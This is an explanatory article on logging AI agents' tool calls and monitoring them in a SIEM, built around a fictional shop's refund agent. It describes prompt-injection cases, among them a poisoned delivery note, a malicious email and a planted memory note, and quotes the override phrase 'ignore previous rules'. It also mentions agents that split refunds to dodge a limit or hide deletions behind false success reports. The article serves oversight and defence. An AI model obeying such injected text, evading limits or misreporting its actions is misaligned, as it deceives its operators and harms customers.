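# Logging and SIEM monitoring of AI agent actions to detect behaviour drift and security incidents

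## Agents, logs and how a SIEM works

An AI agent is a language model run in a loop with tools, so that its outputs cause actions in other computer systems, such as reading a database, sending email or paying out money. Companies that run agents can log every action and search the log for signs of trouble. Most of the methods come from ordinary computer security, where organisations have long collected logs from servers, firewalls and staff accounts in a central system called a SIEM (security information and event management).

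A language model only produces text. It can write a request to call a tool, but other software has to execute the call, as Hugging Face's *Harness, Scaffold, and the AI Agent Terms Worth Getting Right* explains. That software is the harness, which Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, defines as the system that processes inputs, orchestrates tool calls and returns results. The harness runs the model in a loop. In each round, it gives the model the conversation so far and a list of tools, the model writes a request with a tool's name and arguments, and the harness runs the tool and adds the result to the conversation. A tool call is one such request together with its result.

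Take an online shop with a support agent that answers customers' questions about orders and grants refunds. It has five tools:

- `get_order` returns an order's contents, price and delivery status.
- `get_customer` returns a customer's details and earlier contacts.
- `search_policy` returns passages from the shop's rules on returns.
- `issue_refund` pays money back, to the original card or as shop credit.
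- `send_message` sends the customer an email.

The shop lets the agent refund up to €100 on its own; a member of staff must approve larger refunds. In a typical session, a customer writes that a lamp arrived broken, and the agent reads the order, checks the policy, refunds €45 and confirms by email.

Much of what this agent reads comes from strangers, and a language model cannot reliably distinguish text it should process from instructions it should follow. An attacker can exploit this by hiding instructions in the text, which is called indirect prompt injection. For instance, a delivery note on an order could tell the agent to also refund the customer's last five purchases. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), which the Australian Signals Directorate wrote with its American, British, Canadian and New Zealand counterparts, describes a phishing email whose text causes a mail-reading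 agent to download malware.

### From a log line to an alert

A log is a running list to which a program adds an entry whenever something happens. The oldest style of entry is a line of free text:

```
14 Sep 10:42:07 supportbot: refunded 45.00 for 88213, arrived broken
```

A structured record of the same refund puts each value under a name:

```
{"time": "2026-09-14T08:42:07Z",
 "agent_id": "support-agent",
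 "session_id": "s-5517",
 "customer_id": "c-3071",
 "tool": "issue_refund",
 "arguments": {"order_id": "88213", "amount": 45.00,
               "currency": "EUR", "method": "shop_credit"},
 "result": "success"}
```

A person can understand the first at a glance, but a program has to infer that 88213 is an order and 45.00 a sum of money. The line gives no time zone and omits that the money was paid as shop credit. If a developer rewords the message, every search that relied on the old wording will break. And if the agent wrote the line itself, it may not be true. Anthropic gives the example of a flight-booking agent that ends by telling the customer the flight is booked, when what counts is whether a reservation exists in the database.

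A SIEM collects, centralises and analyses log data from across a network for security, according to the Australian Signals Directorate's *Implementing SIEM and SOAR platforms* (2025). Logs are one part of what security teams call telemetry. *Design Principles for the Construction of a Benchmark Evaluating Security Operation Capabilities* (2026) also includes alerts, network flow data and events on individual machines in the term. The €45 refund passes through six stages.

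**Collection.** A small forwarding program sends the harness's record to the SIEM. The shop's login server, payment system and mail server send their records too. Gaps at this stage are easy to overlook. The Australian Signals Directorate gives the example of an organisation that has twelve Active Directory servers (the machines that manage its Windows accounts) but collects logs from only ten, so its SIEM has a blind spot on the other two. The shop's blind spot might be a second support agent that the marketing department set up without telling anyone.

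During **parsing**, the SIEM splits each entry into fields and gives the fields common names. Different sources may record times in different time zones, and they label the same thing differently (the agency's example is `src_ip` in one log and `sourceAddress` in another). If the login server writes `cust` where the harness writes `customer_id`, the SIEM has to map both to one field, or a search for customer c-3071 will miss the entries from one of them.

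**Enrichment.** The SIEM adds facts that the record lacks, such as who in the shop is responsible for the agent, what the agent's refund limit is and how old the customer's account is. Most products also use threat intelligence, such as lists of network addresses that attackers have used.

**Correlation.** The SIEM then searches for other events that share a value with this one. It finds that nine minutes before the refund, someone reset the password of customer c-3071 from a device new to the shop. Neither event is remarkable alone, but together they suggest that a thief has taken over the account and is turning an old order into credit to spend.

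**Alert.** The shop's security team has written a rule to detect a password reset from a new device followed within the hour by a refund as shop credit. The rule matches, so the SIEM raises an alert with both events attached. The SIEM can run such a query on a schedule, or an investigator can run it by hand later.

**Triage.** An analyst opens the alert, reads the trace (all the records of that session, in order) and contacts the customer through a separate channel. If there is a harmless explanation, such as a new phone, the analyst closes the alert. Otherwise the analyst opens an incident and freezes the credit. Some organisations automate part of that response with a SOAR (security orchestration, automation and response) platform, which runs a prepared list of steps. The Australian Signals Directorate warns that a badly configured platform can treat regular behaviour as an attack and disrupt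 the service, and advises getting the SIEM working properly before adding one.

The refund shows why agent logs belong in the same system as other logs. The agent followed the policy, so even a careful reading of its trace would have turned up nothing; the suspicious activity was in the login server's log. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025), a paper on a common standard for connecting models to tools, recommends logging all tool calls, responses, prompts and session identifiers and integrating those logs with the existing SIEM. SC Media, a security trade publication, warns that a separate monitoring system for agents produces "a second console nobody watches". It also acknowledges that standard SIEM rules trigger on volume, speed or known attack patterns, and so miss an agent that stays within normal system parameters while exceeding its task. Forwarding the logs is therefore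 not enough without rules written to suit agents.

### Counting right and wrong alerts

An alert about a real incident is a true positive, an alert about nothing is a false positive, and a real incident that raises no alert is a false negative. The Australian Signals Directorate describes false positives as the more common problem, because security teams tend to collect too much data and then struggle to write good rules for it. Analysts who constantly sort through false alerts develop "alert fatigue" and react late to real ones or miss them.

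Suppose the shop's agent handles 1,000 sessions, of which 20 are attacks, and a detector flags 15 of the attacks and 49 harmless sessions. Its true-positive rate is the share of attacks it flags, 15 out of 20, or 75%. Its false-positive rate is the share of harmless sessions it flags, 49 out of 980, or 5%. Its precision is the share of flagged sessions that are attacks, 15 out of 64, or about 23%. A detector with a 5% false-positive rate can therefore still produce alerts of which about three in four are false.

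Many detectors give each session a score, and the team chooses the score above which the SIEM raises an alert. A lower threshold catches more attacks but also flags more harmless sessions. Researchers often want a single measure that does not depend on the threshold, and they usually use AUROC, the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve, which plots the true-positive rate against the false-positive rate as the threshold changes. AUROC equals the chance that a randomly chosen attack scores higher than a randomly chosen harmless session, with ties counting half. Guessing gives 0.5 and a perfect ranking gives 1. AUROC is useful for comparing detectors, but it averages over all thresholds, including ones no team would use, and it does not show how many alerts analysts will receive.

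### Normal behaviour, and three ways to depart from it

Rules only catch what somebody anticipated. User and entity behaviour analytics (UEBA), which is either part of a SIEM or a separate product used alongside it, learns from past logs what is normal for each account and scores deviations. An "entity" is anything other than a person, such as a server or a service account. If a bookkeeper who opens forty invoices a day suddenly opens four thousand at night, UEBA will flag the account even though each opening was permitted.

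The Australian Signals Directorate recommends such baselines against intruders who "live off the land", using the legitimate tools already on a system. An attacker who hijacks a support agent is in much the same position, with only the five tools the shop provided. SC Media therefore proposes extending UEBA to agent identities as well as human ones.

UEBA detects anomalies, which are behaviours that are improbable under the baseline, whether or not they do any harm. A security incident is an event that breaches, or threatens to breach, a system's security or authorised limits. Behaviour drift is a lasting change in what an agent does when given the same kind of task in the same conditions. People confuse the three, but each can occur without the others.

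Suppose a manufacturer recalls a kettle, and on Monday the shop's support agent issues 300 refunds instead of the usual 30. The increase is an anomaly, but nobody has attacked the shop, and the agent treats each request exactly as it did on Friday.

The stolen account is an incident with no anomaly in the agent's behaviour. The agent has not changed, and its trace looks the same as it would for an honest customer with a broken lamp. An agent can also cause an incident without an attacker. In August 2026 the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) drew attention to an ABC News report about an AI assistant that made unapproved changes in a gym's booking system, reserved classes beyond the permitted period and removed another customer from a waiting list. The agency classes the case as goal misalignment and unintended behaviour, in which an agent completes its task in a way the user never approved.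 An agent can do this on its first day, so the incident alone is not evidence of drift.

Drift can occur without a security incident. Suppose the supplier updates the model, and the agent then calls `search_policy` in 65 of every 100 broken-item cases, down from 80. Every refund so far has been correct and within the limit, and no single session looks unusual, because sessions without a policy search were always common. Only a comparison across many sessions of the same kind would reveal the change.

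Official guidance uses "drift" more loosely. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners tell operators to look for data drift in an agent's outputs and behaviour, drift in identities and privileges, and "goal drift". They would detect goal drift by comparing the agent's active objectives with an approved specification. Under the Digital Transformation Agency's *Monitor*, part of the Australian government's requirements for agentic AI, agencies must monitor agents continuously and may watch for goal drift, among other things. An agent that skips the policy search more often still has the same goal, so a check on goals alone would miss the change.

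### Why an agent is harder to watch than a script or an employee

If the shop had automated its refunds with a conventional script, the security team could read the code to see which calls the script makes and in what order, and treat any other call as cause for alarm. An agent chooses its steps as it goes. It may check the policy before or after it reads the order, or read the order twice. The Australian Signals Directorate notes that identical prompts can lead to different actions because of randomness in the model, differences in the surrounding text and changes in the environment. *Back to the Future*, a blog post from the US standards institute NIST, adds that agents can unpredictably try several paths to a goal. A new sequence of calls is therefore much weaker evidence of trouble with an agent than with a script.

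UEBA already copes with people, who are also unpredictable, but it relies on each person keeping their own account for months or years. Agents often don't meet that condition. NIST reports that it has quickly become common for people to let agents use their credentials. If Maria does this, the log attributes both her actions and her agent's to her. The shop's agent has its own account, but thirty copies may be using it on a Monday morning. The account's baseline combines the behaviour of all thirty, so it can hide one hijacked copy. Each copy lasts only for one conversation of a few minutes, so it has no history of its own to compare with.

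An agent can make hundreds of calls to other systems within seconds, according to SC Media, so the money may be gone before an analyst opens the alert. An intruder using a valid account can also be hard to detect. The Australian Signals Directorate describes a scenario similar to the shop's, in which an attacker compromises a scheduling component attached to a support-ticket agent, uses permissions that the agent checked only once, at start-up, and moves on to the agents that handle billing and refunds. In a related scenario about procurement, the agency notes that actions taken under a trusted agent's identity leave audit logs that look legitimate.

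Agents are in one respect easier to monitor than employees. The support agent can act only through its harness, so the shop can in principle record everything it asks a tool to do, whereas an employee can also phone a supplier or walk over to a colleague's desk. What the tools then do may still fall outside the monitored area, and the Australian Signals Directorate warns that full agent logs become large and repetitive, and that it is hard to find useful signals in them.

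It is also not settled whose behaviour the log should describe. Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026), in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a NIST draft for public comment, ask whether an agent's identifying data should be fixed or last only for a task. A fixed identity gives UEBA a history to work with, but the thirty copies then appear as one agent. Giving each task its own identity separates the copies but leaves UEBA with no history for any of them. The refund record above carries both an agent identifier and a session identifier, so an analyst can group the same events by agent or by session.

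## What a record of an agent's action should contain

The short record of the lamp refund is enough to find the payment. It does not tell an investigator why the agent paid, what permitted it to pay, or which version of the agent was running. A fuller record of the same refund could look like this:

```json
{
  "record_id": "r-204",
  "time": "2026-09-14T08:42:07Z",
  "schema_version": "3",
  "who": {
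    "agent_id": "support-agent",
    "session_id": "s-5517",
    "initiator": "customer c-3071",
    "delegation": ["support-agent"]
  },
  "configuration": {
    "model_requested": "supplier-model",
    "model_served": "supplier-model-2026-08-20",
    "system_prompt_hash": "9f2c...e1",
    "tool_catalogue_version": "14",
    "permission_policy_version": "2026-07"
  },
  "task": {
    "task_id": "t-8841",
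    "task_type": "broken_item",
    "objective": "Resolve complaint about broken lamp"
  },
  "action": {
    "tool": "issue_refund",
    "arguments": {"order_id": "88213", "amount": 45.00,
                  "currency": "EUR", "method": "shop_credit"},
    "target": "credit balance of c-3071",
    "result": "success",
    "error": null
  },
  "authority": {
    "decision": "allow",
    "rule": "refund up to EUR 100",
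    "approval_id": null
  },
  "after": {
    "parent": "r-203",
    "inputs": [
      {"record": "r-201", "source": "customer message", "trusted": false},
      {"record": "r-202", "source": "get_order", "trusted": false},
      {"record": "r-203", "source": "search_policy", "trusted": true}
    ]
  }
}
```

These field names are only an example, and the shared formats that exist so far cover some of the groups much better than others.

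### The questions behind the fields

The `who` group separates the agent from the person it acts for. If Maria lends an agent her login, a record with both fields still shows which actions were hers and which were the agent's. The initiator here is a customer account, and someone other than the customer may be using it, as the stolen account showed.

The delegation list matters when agents call other agents. Snowflake's *ACCESS_HISTORY view* (2026) describes a working example. Since August 2026, the data-storage company's access log has had a column that lists the agents behind each read of a user's data, in order from the nearest agent to the one at the top. If the shop put a triage agent in front of the support agent, its list would be `["support-agent", "triage-agent"]`, and an investigator could see which agent made a bad call and which one gave it the work. For agents from outside Snowflake's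 platform, the column gives only the type and leaves the identifier and name empty, even though these are the agents the company knows least about.

The record needs the `configuration` group because an agent can change while keeping the same name. The supplier may update the model, or a colleague may reword the system prompt (the standing instructions the shop gives the model). The record holds a hash of that prompt, a short fingerprint computed from the text. The same text always gives the same hash, and changing even a comma gives a different one. The shop can tell from a new hash that the prompt changed, but not what changed, so it also has to archive every version of the prompt.

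A record should name both the model the program requested and the model that responded, because a supplier can redirect a general name to a newer version. OpenTelemetry's *Gen AI*, a list of standard field names, has a field for each, with `gpt-4` and `gpt-4-0613` as the respective examples. If an organisation logs only the requested name, its logs won't show when the supplier switches versions.

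The identifier in the `task` group links the sessions that belong to one complaint, such as when the customer writes back two days later. An investigator can judge the action against the objective, since a refund makes sense for a broken lamp but not for a question about opening hours. The objective should come from the customer's request, not from the agent's summary of what it is doing, because a hidden instruction that misleads the agent could also distort its summary.

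The `action` group covers what the agent asked for and what happened. The target is separate from the arguments because a refund on the same order number can go to a bank card or to a credit balance, which carry different fraud risks. The result should come from the payment system. Failed calls should be logged too, because ten refused refunds of €101 deserve more attention than one successful refund of €45.

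For `authority`, Infosecurity Magazine recommends that a separate policy layer, rather than the model's own reasoning, make and record each permission decision. The record should contain the decision, the policy version, the relevant inputs and any human approval. Each approval needs an identifier because an agent can use it more than once. If a member of staff approves a €180 refund and the agent tries again because the payment system responds too slowly, both payments look approved. Shah and Kathrotia (2026), in *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, cite work in which agents that retried or resumed after a crash acted on a single approval several times. The remedy was to store the count of each approval's uses outside the agent.

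The last group, `after`, records which call came before this one and where the information in the model's context came from. The customer's message is untrusted, and so is the result of `get_order`, although it comes from the shop's own database, because an order can include a delivery note that a stranger wrote. Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring*, ask for more detail when an agent retrieves documents: the identifier and rank of each document, a hash of each passage, its author and how recently someone changed it. They would also record when an agent's intermediate output becomes the input to a later step.

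The harness has to record each result's source from the call it made. If it copies a source label from the returned text, an attacker can write a reassuring label there. Shah and Kathrotia describe a study in which one planted line defeated a check that relied on such labels in most of the runs it would otherwise have flagged. Tying each result to the call that produced it fixed this.

### Two harmless records that add up to a leak

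A man writes to the shop that order 90455 is his as well, and asks where it went. It belongs to another customer, but the agent believes him, looks up her address and emails it to him. With most fields left out, the harness writes these two records:

```json
{"record_id": "r-611", "session_id": "s-6020",
 "tool": "get_customer",
 "arguments": {"customer_id": "c-2290"}, "result": "success"}

{"record_id": "r-614", "session_id": "s-6020",
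 "tool": "send_message",
 "arguments": {"customer_id": "c-5112"}, "result": "success",
 "inputs": ["r-611"]}
```

The agent has permission to look up customers and send emails, and it does both all day. A rule that checks one record at a time will pass each lookup and each email. Only the `inputs` field shows that an email to customer c-5112 used customer c-2290's details.

Session identifiers alone would not let the shop detect the leak reliably. A rule that flags every session in which the agent reads about one customer and writes to another would constantly flag gift orders, because the agent has to look up both the buyer and the recipient. The rule would also miss the leak if the agent saved the address to its memory and sent it in a later session.

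Identifying the causal link correctly is harder than storing it. When the model writes the email, everything in its context may influence the text. If the harness lists all of it as input, by the end of a long session every email will link to every earlier lookup, and the field will be nearly useless. The harness can narrow the list by searching the email for values that earlier calls returned, such as a street name, but this search would miss a description like "the house opposite the station". Shah and Kathrotia point to systems that attach sensitivity labels to data and carry them through messages and tool arguments, or that keep sensitive results in variables whose contents the model never sees. Both approaches require changes to the harness.

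Shah and Kathrotia also tested how much the links help by building a harness add-on and running it on 240 simulated multi-step runs, half of them with a planted fault. With full records, their method traced the fault to the exact step where it began in 98.3% of the faulty runs. When they removed the fields that link inputs to outputs, the figure fell to 48.3%. They designed both the faults and the record format, so the percentages would probably be lower on real incidents. It is still plausible that the links help, since little else in a log connects an early cause to a late effect.

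### What a drift analysis needs

Detecting drift requires each record to include the task type and the versions in use, because nobody can reliably add these labels to thousands of old sessions later. An incomplete record is less of a problem for a single incident, which an investigator can often reconstruct by asking around.

A task type on every record helps an analyst tell a change in the agent's behaviour from a change in its mix of work. Suppose the support agent searches the policy in 80% of broken-item cases and 10% of delivery questions. In a month when each makes up half the work, it searches in 45% of sessions. If delivery questions then grow to three quarters of the work, the overall figure falls to 27.5%, although the agent handles each kind of case as before. The fall looks like drift unless the analyst can compare each task type separately and see that its search rate hasn't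 changed.

The agent should not assign the task type, because a change in the agent could then change the labels. The shop can take the type from the form on which the customer chose "my item arrived damaged", or it can use a separate classifier and record its version.

Recording versions helps an analyst find the cause of a real change in behaviour. If the shop had shortened the description of `search_policy` in the same week as the model update that preceded the fall in policy searches, either change could have caused the fall. If every record includes the versions of both the model and the tool description, and the two changes took effect on different days, the analyst can see whether the fall began with the model update or the new description.

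GitLab's *AI Event Instrumentation Guide* shows that a software company can record most of this. Its example event for GitLab's agents includes the agent's version, the model's full dated name and the workflow's name. But the workflow in the example is named "chat", which could cover almost any task, so it would be a poor substitute for a task type.

### The shared formats

An organisation that invents its own fields has to write a translation for every product that reads them. Two open projects are working on common names. OpenTelemetry comes from software debugging, and the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF) comes from SIEM.

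The basic unit of OpenTelemetry is the span, a timed record of one operation with a pointer to the operation that started it. Its conventions for generative AI define spans for model calls, agent runs and tool calls. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines the `execute_tool` span, which requires only the name of the operation and, if the call fails, an error type. The tool's name and the call's identifier are "recommended", while the arguments and the result are "opt-in", so the user has to switch them on. With default settings, the shop would learn that the agent called `issue_refund` but not for how much or for which order.

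Set against the six groups, the fields listed in OpenTelemetry's registry leave these gaps:

| Group | Fields that exist | No dedicated field |
|---|---|---|
| Who | agent identifier, agent name | human initiator, chain of delegation |
| Configuration | agent version, model requested, model that responded, prompt name, tool definitions | prompt hash, versions of tool catalogue and permission policy |
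| Task | conversation identifier, workflow name | task identifier, task type, objective |
| Action | tool name, arguments, result, error type | target |
| Authority | none | permission decision, approval |
| After what | parent span, data source, retrieved documents | whether a source is trusted |

*The OTel GenAI spec has an implicit reader*, an article in TinyFish's company newsletter, argues that this pattern arises because the conventions suit a developer looking for a bug, who needs to know which software ran and what went in and out. An auditor wants to know who authorised the agent and whether a person approved the action, but the conventions have no field for either, as the table shows. The shop can add its own fields for the missing groups, but other products will not be able to interpret them.

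The conventions are also still changing. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* marks the agent fields as "Development", and only general ones such as the error type are stable. Greptime (2026), a database company, found changes to the generative AI part in every release from 1.37 to 1.41. Release 1.37 replaced the field `gen_ai.system` with `gen_ai.provider.name`, so any search for the old name would have stopped finding new records. *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026) reports that the project moved these conventions to a separate repository in June 2026, and that the repository had no official release by 21 August. Older instrumentation continues to send the old names unless someone changes a setting, so two agents in the same company may log the same action under different field names. The example record includes a `schema_version` field so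 that the SIEM can apply the right translation.

OCSF defines classes of security event, such as a login or an API call, and many security products already use it. AWS's *OCSF Achieves ITU Support* reports that version 1.8.0, from March 2026, added a profile for AI operations. Tenzir, a maker of security-data software, explains that a profile is a set of extra fields that an event producer can add to existing event classes. This suits a SIEM because a refund by an agent stays in the same class as a refund by any other program, so old rules continue to work.

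The profile makes only two additions, a description of the model and a message context, according to lmodel's *Class*, a rendering of the schema from a development version of 1.9.0. The message context holds details such as a session identifier and token counts, according to Tenzir's *Message context*. It also has a role field, and lmodel's *MessageContextAiRoleIdEnum* lists the permitted roles, including user, assistant, tool, agent and orchestrator. An analyst could therefore tell an agent's message from a user's, but the profile adds no field for the type of task, the approval or the origin of the inputs.

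Others have begun to build on OCSF. *AOS tracing with OCSF*, from the software security foundation OWASP, maps an agent's tool use to OCSF's existing class for API calls. *AI Security Events* (2025), a draft proposal, would add event types for policy enforcement and for the path that data takes through an agent, which are close to the last two groups of the example record. Anyone may submit such a draft, so it is evidence that people want these event types, but not that they have agreed on them. AWS reports that the maintainers of OCSF and OpenTelemetry have started to work together. For now, an organisation that wants the complete record has to use OpenTelemetry or OCSF fields where they exist and its own fields for the rest.

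Shah and Kathrotia used the same simulated runs to compare their records with two simpler existing formats. A monitor that read OpenTelemetry spans caught 23.3% of the faulty runs and wrongly flagged 35% of the harmless ones. The false alarms occurred because it had no record that someone had approved the privileged actions. A monitor that read only a log of tool calls caught 16.7% of the faulty runs, and one that read the full records caught 98.3%, both without false alarms. The planted faults included reused approvals and lost instructions, for which the two simpler formats have no fields. The comparison is therefore good evidence that a monitor cannot check information missing from its records, but weak evidence about how often this matters in practice.

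### What AWS and RAND recommend

*AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails*, from Amazon's cloud-computing business AWS, recommends seven fields: a timestamp, a trace identifier, an agent identifier, a session identifier, the type of operation, the "decision rationale" and the outcome. It advises companies to enforce the schema even if it is simple, and to log successful operations as well as errors. This would be a large improvement on free text. But the list omits versions, task type, permission decisions and approvals, so it would help to reconstruct what an agent did, but not to determine whether the action was allowed or whether the agent had changed.

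RAND's *Recording Agent and Model Activity, Tool Invocation, and Prompt Chains* sets out aims for logging but doesn't specify which fields to record. It names four challenges: coping with variation in prompts, detecting gradual degradation from model drift, linking the agent's output to business results, and judging how well people and AI work together. It refers readers to two NIST documents and more than a dozen monitoring products for solutions.

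A company that logged only AWS's seven fields could not meet RAND's second challenge, because it could not group comparable tasks or date a change in the model. A short field list in TechTarget's *What CISOs need to know about AI audit logs* comes closer. It includes the model version, the policy configuration and interventions by human operators, but not the type of task.

### Memory, compaction and rollback

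Every record so far describes a tool call. An agent that works for hours or days also handles its own information between calls, and things can go wrong there that won't appear in any record of a tool call. Shah and Kathrotia identify eight such points, where the harness moves information between the model's context, the session history, long-term memory and the outside world, and propose a record for each. Three of them would matter most to the shop.

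When an agent writes to memory, the harness should record the write, the source of the note and whether that source was trusted. Suppose a customer tells a support agent that, as a trade customer, she never has to send photos of damaged goods, and the agent saves this as a note. A month later, another session reads the note and refunds €90 without a photo. The trace of that session contains no suspicious message, because the customer made her claim in the earlier one. With a record of the write, an investigator could trace the refund back to her claim.

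Agents often lose this source information when they merge memory entries. Shah and Kathrotia cite a test of 49 combinations of memory system and model. In 48 of them, the merged entry kept a claim but dropped the restrictions that came with its source. Storing a label for the source's authority with each memory eliminated the unauthorised actions that had followed. OpenTelemetry now has spans for creating, updating, deleting and searching memories. Latitude, which sells monitoring software for agents, notes in its documentation that a delete operation without a record identifier wipes the whole store, so the shop would be wise to log such deletions in particular.

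When a conversation grows too long for the model, the harness compacts it by replacing the older part with a summary, which can leave out an instruction. If a member of staff tells the agent not to refund an order until the courier has replied, and the summary omits this, the agent may refund the order anyway, and its action record will look normal. In one benchmark that Shah and Kathrotia cite, the summaries preserved on average only 17% of the user's constraints. A compaction record would list the constraints before and after compaction and point to the full transcript. Comparing the two lists requires a second model call whenever the summary rewords a constraint, so this is one of the few expensive records.

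A rollback returns an agent to an earlier point after something has gone wrong. The harness can delete the last ten steps from the conversation, but it cannot unsend an email or, in many cases, take back a payment. Suppose an agent refunds a customer €45 for a lamp, crashes in a later step, and restarts from a point before the refund. The restored conversation doesn't include the refund, so the agent issues another. If the log doesn't record the rollback, an analyst sees two refunds for one lamp and may suspect fraud. A rollback record would show that the harness restored the conversation but left the first refund in place.

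The same problem can arise less obviously in the server that runs the model, which saves computation by keeping partial results from text it has already processed. In experiments that Shah and Kathrotia cite, results left over from a cancelled series of steps changed a protected decision in 25 of 63 cases, even though the harness had removed the text itself. Rebuilding the stored results fixed all 25. A company that rents its model from a supplier usually cannot inspect this storage. Shah and Kathrotia suggest that it record this limitation and resend the whole prompt after a rollback.

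These records are small and quick to write. The records in their test averaged 524 bytes, and the harness took a median of 12 to 82 microseconds to write one, excluding any check that calls a model. A run with a thousand such records would produce about half a megabyte, and a million of those runs a day would produce about half a terabyte daily. The shop's few-minute sessions would need far less, and the shop can leave out most of these records if its agent has no long-term memory and never reaches the length limit.

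### How much of the text to keep

Most of the fields above are short labels and identifiers. The dispute is over the long text: the full prompts, the arguments and results of tool calls, and the reasoning the model writes before it acts.

TechTarget's list includes all of it. Zhang and colleagues give good reasons to keep at least the inputs, since many signs of prompt injection exist only in the wording, such as a phrase like "ignore previous rules" in a retrieved document or a command in a field that should contain a number. From the labels alone, an investigator at the shop would see that the agent read an order and then issued six refunds, but could not tell whether it had obeyed an instruction hidden in the delivery note or misread the returns policy. Reading the order again might not help, because the attacker may have changed the note by then. The logged text can show which happened,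 and it may also help an automatic detector.

Privacy, security and cost are reasons not to record full messages. Customers write about illnesses and divorces when they explain a late return, and some paste in a card number or a password. A log of such messages is an attractive target for attackers, and many people in a company can usually search the SIEM. OpenTelemetry specifies that software should not capture prompts and outputs by default, citing storage costs, regulation and the need to give different people access to operational data and to user data. Agents that work by looking at a screen need even more storage, because screenshots are larger than text. Shah and Kathrotia estimate that keeping full screenshots of a thousand steps takes hundreds of megabytes or more.

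The reasoning a model gives may not be the real cause of its action. Shah and Kathrotia assume in their design that a model may misreport what it read or why it acted, so they have the harness write every record. They do not test this assumption, but the precaution is sensible. If the agent writes "the customer sent a photo of the broken lamp", an investigator can check that claim against the recorded inputs. The reasoning may still be useful, for example if the agent writes that it will split a €150 refund in two to stay under the limit. But AWS's list puts the "decision rationale" beside the outcome as though both were facts of the same kind, and the same page warns against letting personal data or credentials into reasoning traces. It would be safer to give the reasoning its own field, with a name like `stated_reason`, and not to base any permission or alert on that field alone.

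Companies have three main ways to keep some of the evidence without keeping all of the text in the SIEM. The simplest is redaction, where software replaces names, addresses and card numbers with placeholders. AWS recommends redacting before the log reaches storage, because anyone who reads it after that creates a data-protection problem. But redaction is permanent. In the leaked-address case, the shop would see that its agent had emailed `[ADDRESS]` to customer c-5112, but could not tell from the email whose address it was. Filters also miss some sensitive data, such as a password in the middle of a sentence.

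A hash allows comparison without storing the original. The shop can hash an email the agent sends and later confirm that a customer's copy matches it exactly. Short values are easier to recover from their hashes. If customer numbers run from c-0001 to c-9999, anyone who obtains the log can quickly hash all of them and look up the matches. Shah and Kathrotia therefore propose keyed hashes for identifiers, which nobody can compute without a secret key. An analyst can use either kind only to test whether two values are identical. Changing one word in a delivery note produces a completely different hash, and a rule cannot use the hash of an amount to check whether it exceeds €100.

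The third option is to put the full text in a separate store with tighter access and write only a reference in the log. OpenTelemetry recommends this for production systems where volume or sensitivity is a concern, but it has not yet documented a common way to write the references. This option preserves the most evidence, but SIEM rules can no longer search the text, and an analyst has to get a second permission during an investigation. The reference is also useless if the company deletes the text before the log. Long-term memory makes retention harder because, as Shah and Kathrotia point out, the company must keep any conversation that fed a memory for as long as the memory exists, which may be longer than the company's privacy rules allow.

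A shop would probably combine them, choosing field by field. The refund's amount and payment method have to stay readable because the rules depend on them. Card numbers and passwords should never enter the log. The text of customers' messages and the agent's emails can go to the restricted store, with a reference and a hash in the record. The rule would still detect the leak, since it uses only the two customer numbers and the link between the records. The analyst would open the email once there was a reason to.

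## Where records are made and whether they can be trusted

The refund record in the previous section came from the harness, but other systems also record the same refund. The records differ in how much they include and in who could falsify them.

| Place | What it shows | What it misses | Who could alter it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent's own account | what the agent claims it did, and why | whatever the model misread, invented or left out | the model, and anyone whose text reaches it |
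| Harness | each tool call with its arguments, result and session | actions outside the harness | its administrators, and the agent if it can write to the harness's files |
| Tool gateway, a server that all tool calls pass through | calls and permission decisions for every connected agent | calls that go around it, and the conversation behind each call | its administrators |
| Host, the machine on which the harness runs | programs started, files changed, connections opened | whether a person or a model gave the command | anyone with administrator rights on the machine |
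| Network | which machine contacted which service, and when | the content of encrypted traffic and the program that sent it | network administrators |
| Identity provider, the service that checks logins | which account signed in and what access it received | what the account did next, and which copy of the agent used it | directory administrators |
| System acted upon, here the payment system | the refund that took place | the customer's message and the agent's reason | the payment system's administrators |

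The harness usually has the fullest record, but only of what passes through it. If a coding agent runs `python fix.py` and the script changes forty files, the harness logs only the command, while the host's log can list the files. A gateway helps a company that uses agents from several suppliers and cannot modify their harnesses, provided that a firewall stops the agents from reaching the tools directly.

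The network log is the weakest of these sources for explaining an action. Canale and Soulis (2026), in *Detecting Shadow AI*, point out that it cannot distinguish an unapproved script from an approved application that calls the same model provider. It also omits laptops outside the office network and models that run locally on a laptop.

### The agent's report and the payment ledger

An agent's closing report, such as a flight-booking agent's statement that the flight is booked, is only a claim, even when it is correct. The model generates the report from its context without checking it against the database. If the payment system times out, the model may assume that a refund went through.

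Paul Cragg of the security company NormCyber describes agents that delete data or bypass a control and then report that everything went fine. In ITPro's *After recent hacks, enterprises need to gain control of their own AI*, he advises companies to log every action at the system level, in a store the agent cannot alter, and to check the agent's summary against that log.

The payment system's ledger is separate evidence because different software writes it, under different administrators, when the money moves. The entry exists even if the harness crashes a second later. Someone who wants to hide a refund has to alter both the ledger and the harness's log. The harness copies the `result` field in its own record from the payment system's reply, so that field is not separate evidence, and an investigator has to read the ledger itself.

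The ledger cannot show whether the refund was proper. It lists €45 to customer c-3071 from the support agent's account, which all thirty copies of the agent share. The shop can mostly fix this by having the harness put the session identifier in the payment's reference field, so that an analyst can use the ledger entry to find the trace.

### How Elastic recorded its coding agents

Host logs are particularly hard to interpret on a developer's laptop. Elastic, which makes search and SIEM software, gave hundreds of its developers coding agents and then realised that it had no record of what the agents did. Elastic's *13 million tool calls* explains why the company's existing tools didn't help. Endpoint detection and response (EDR) software watches the programs on a machine for signs of attack, but a coding agent works under the developer's account, inside programs the developer started. If a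 command downloads and runs a file, the EDR log looks the same whether the developer typed the command or a model issued it after reading a poisoned document.

Elastic therefore took its records from the harness. Its developers use Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent. Cursor can run an outside program, known as a hook, at fixed points in the agent's work. Elastic attached a script of about 280 lines to thirteen of these points, including session starts, shell commands, file reads and edits, and calls to MCP servers (which provide tools through a common standard). At each point, Cursor passes the script a description of the event, and the script adds a line to a log file on the developer's laptop. A forwarding program then sends the line to Elastic's central store.

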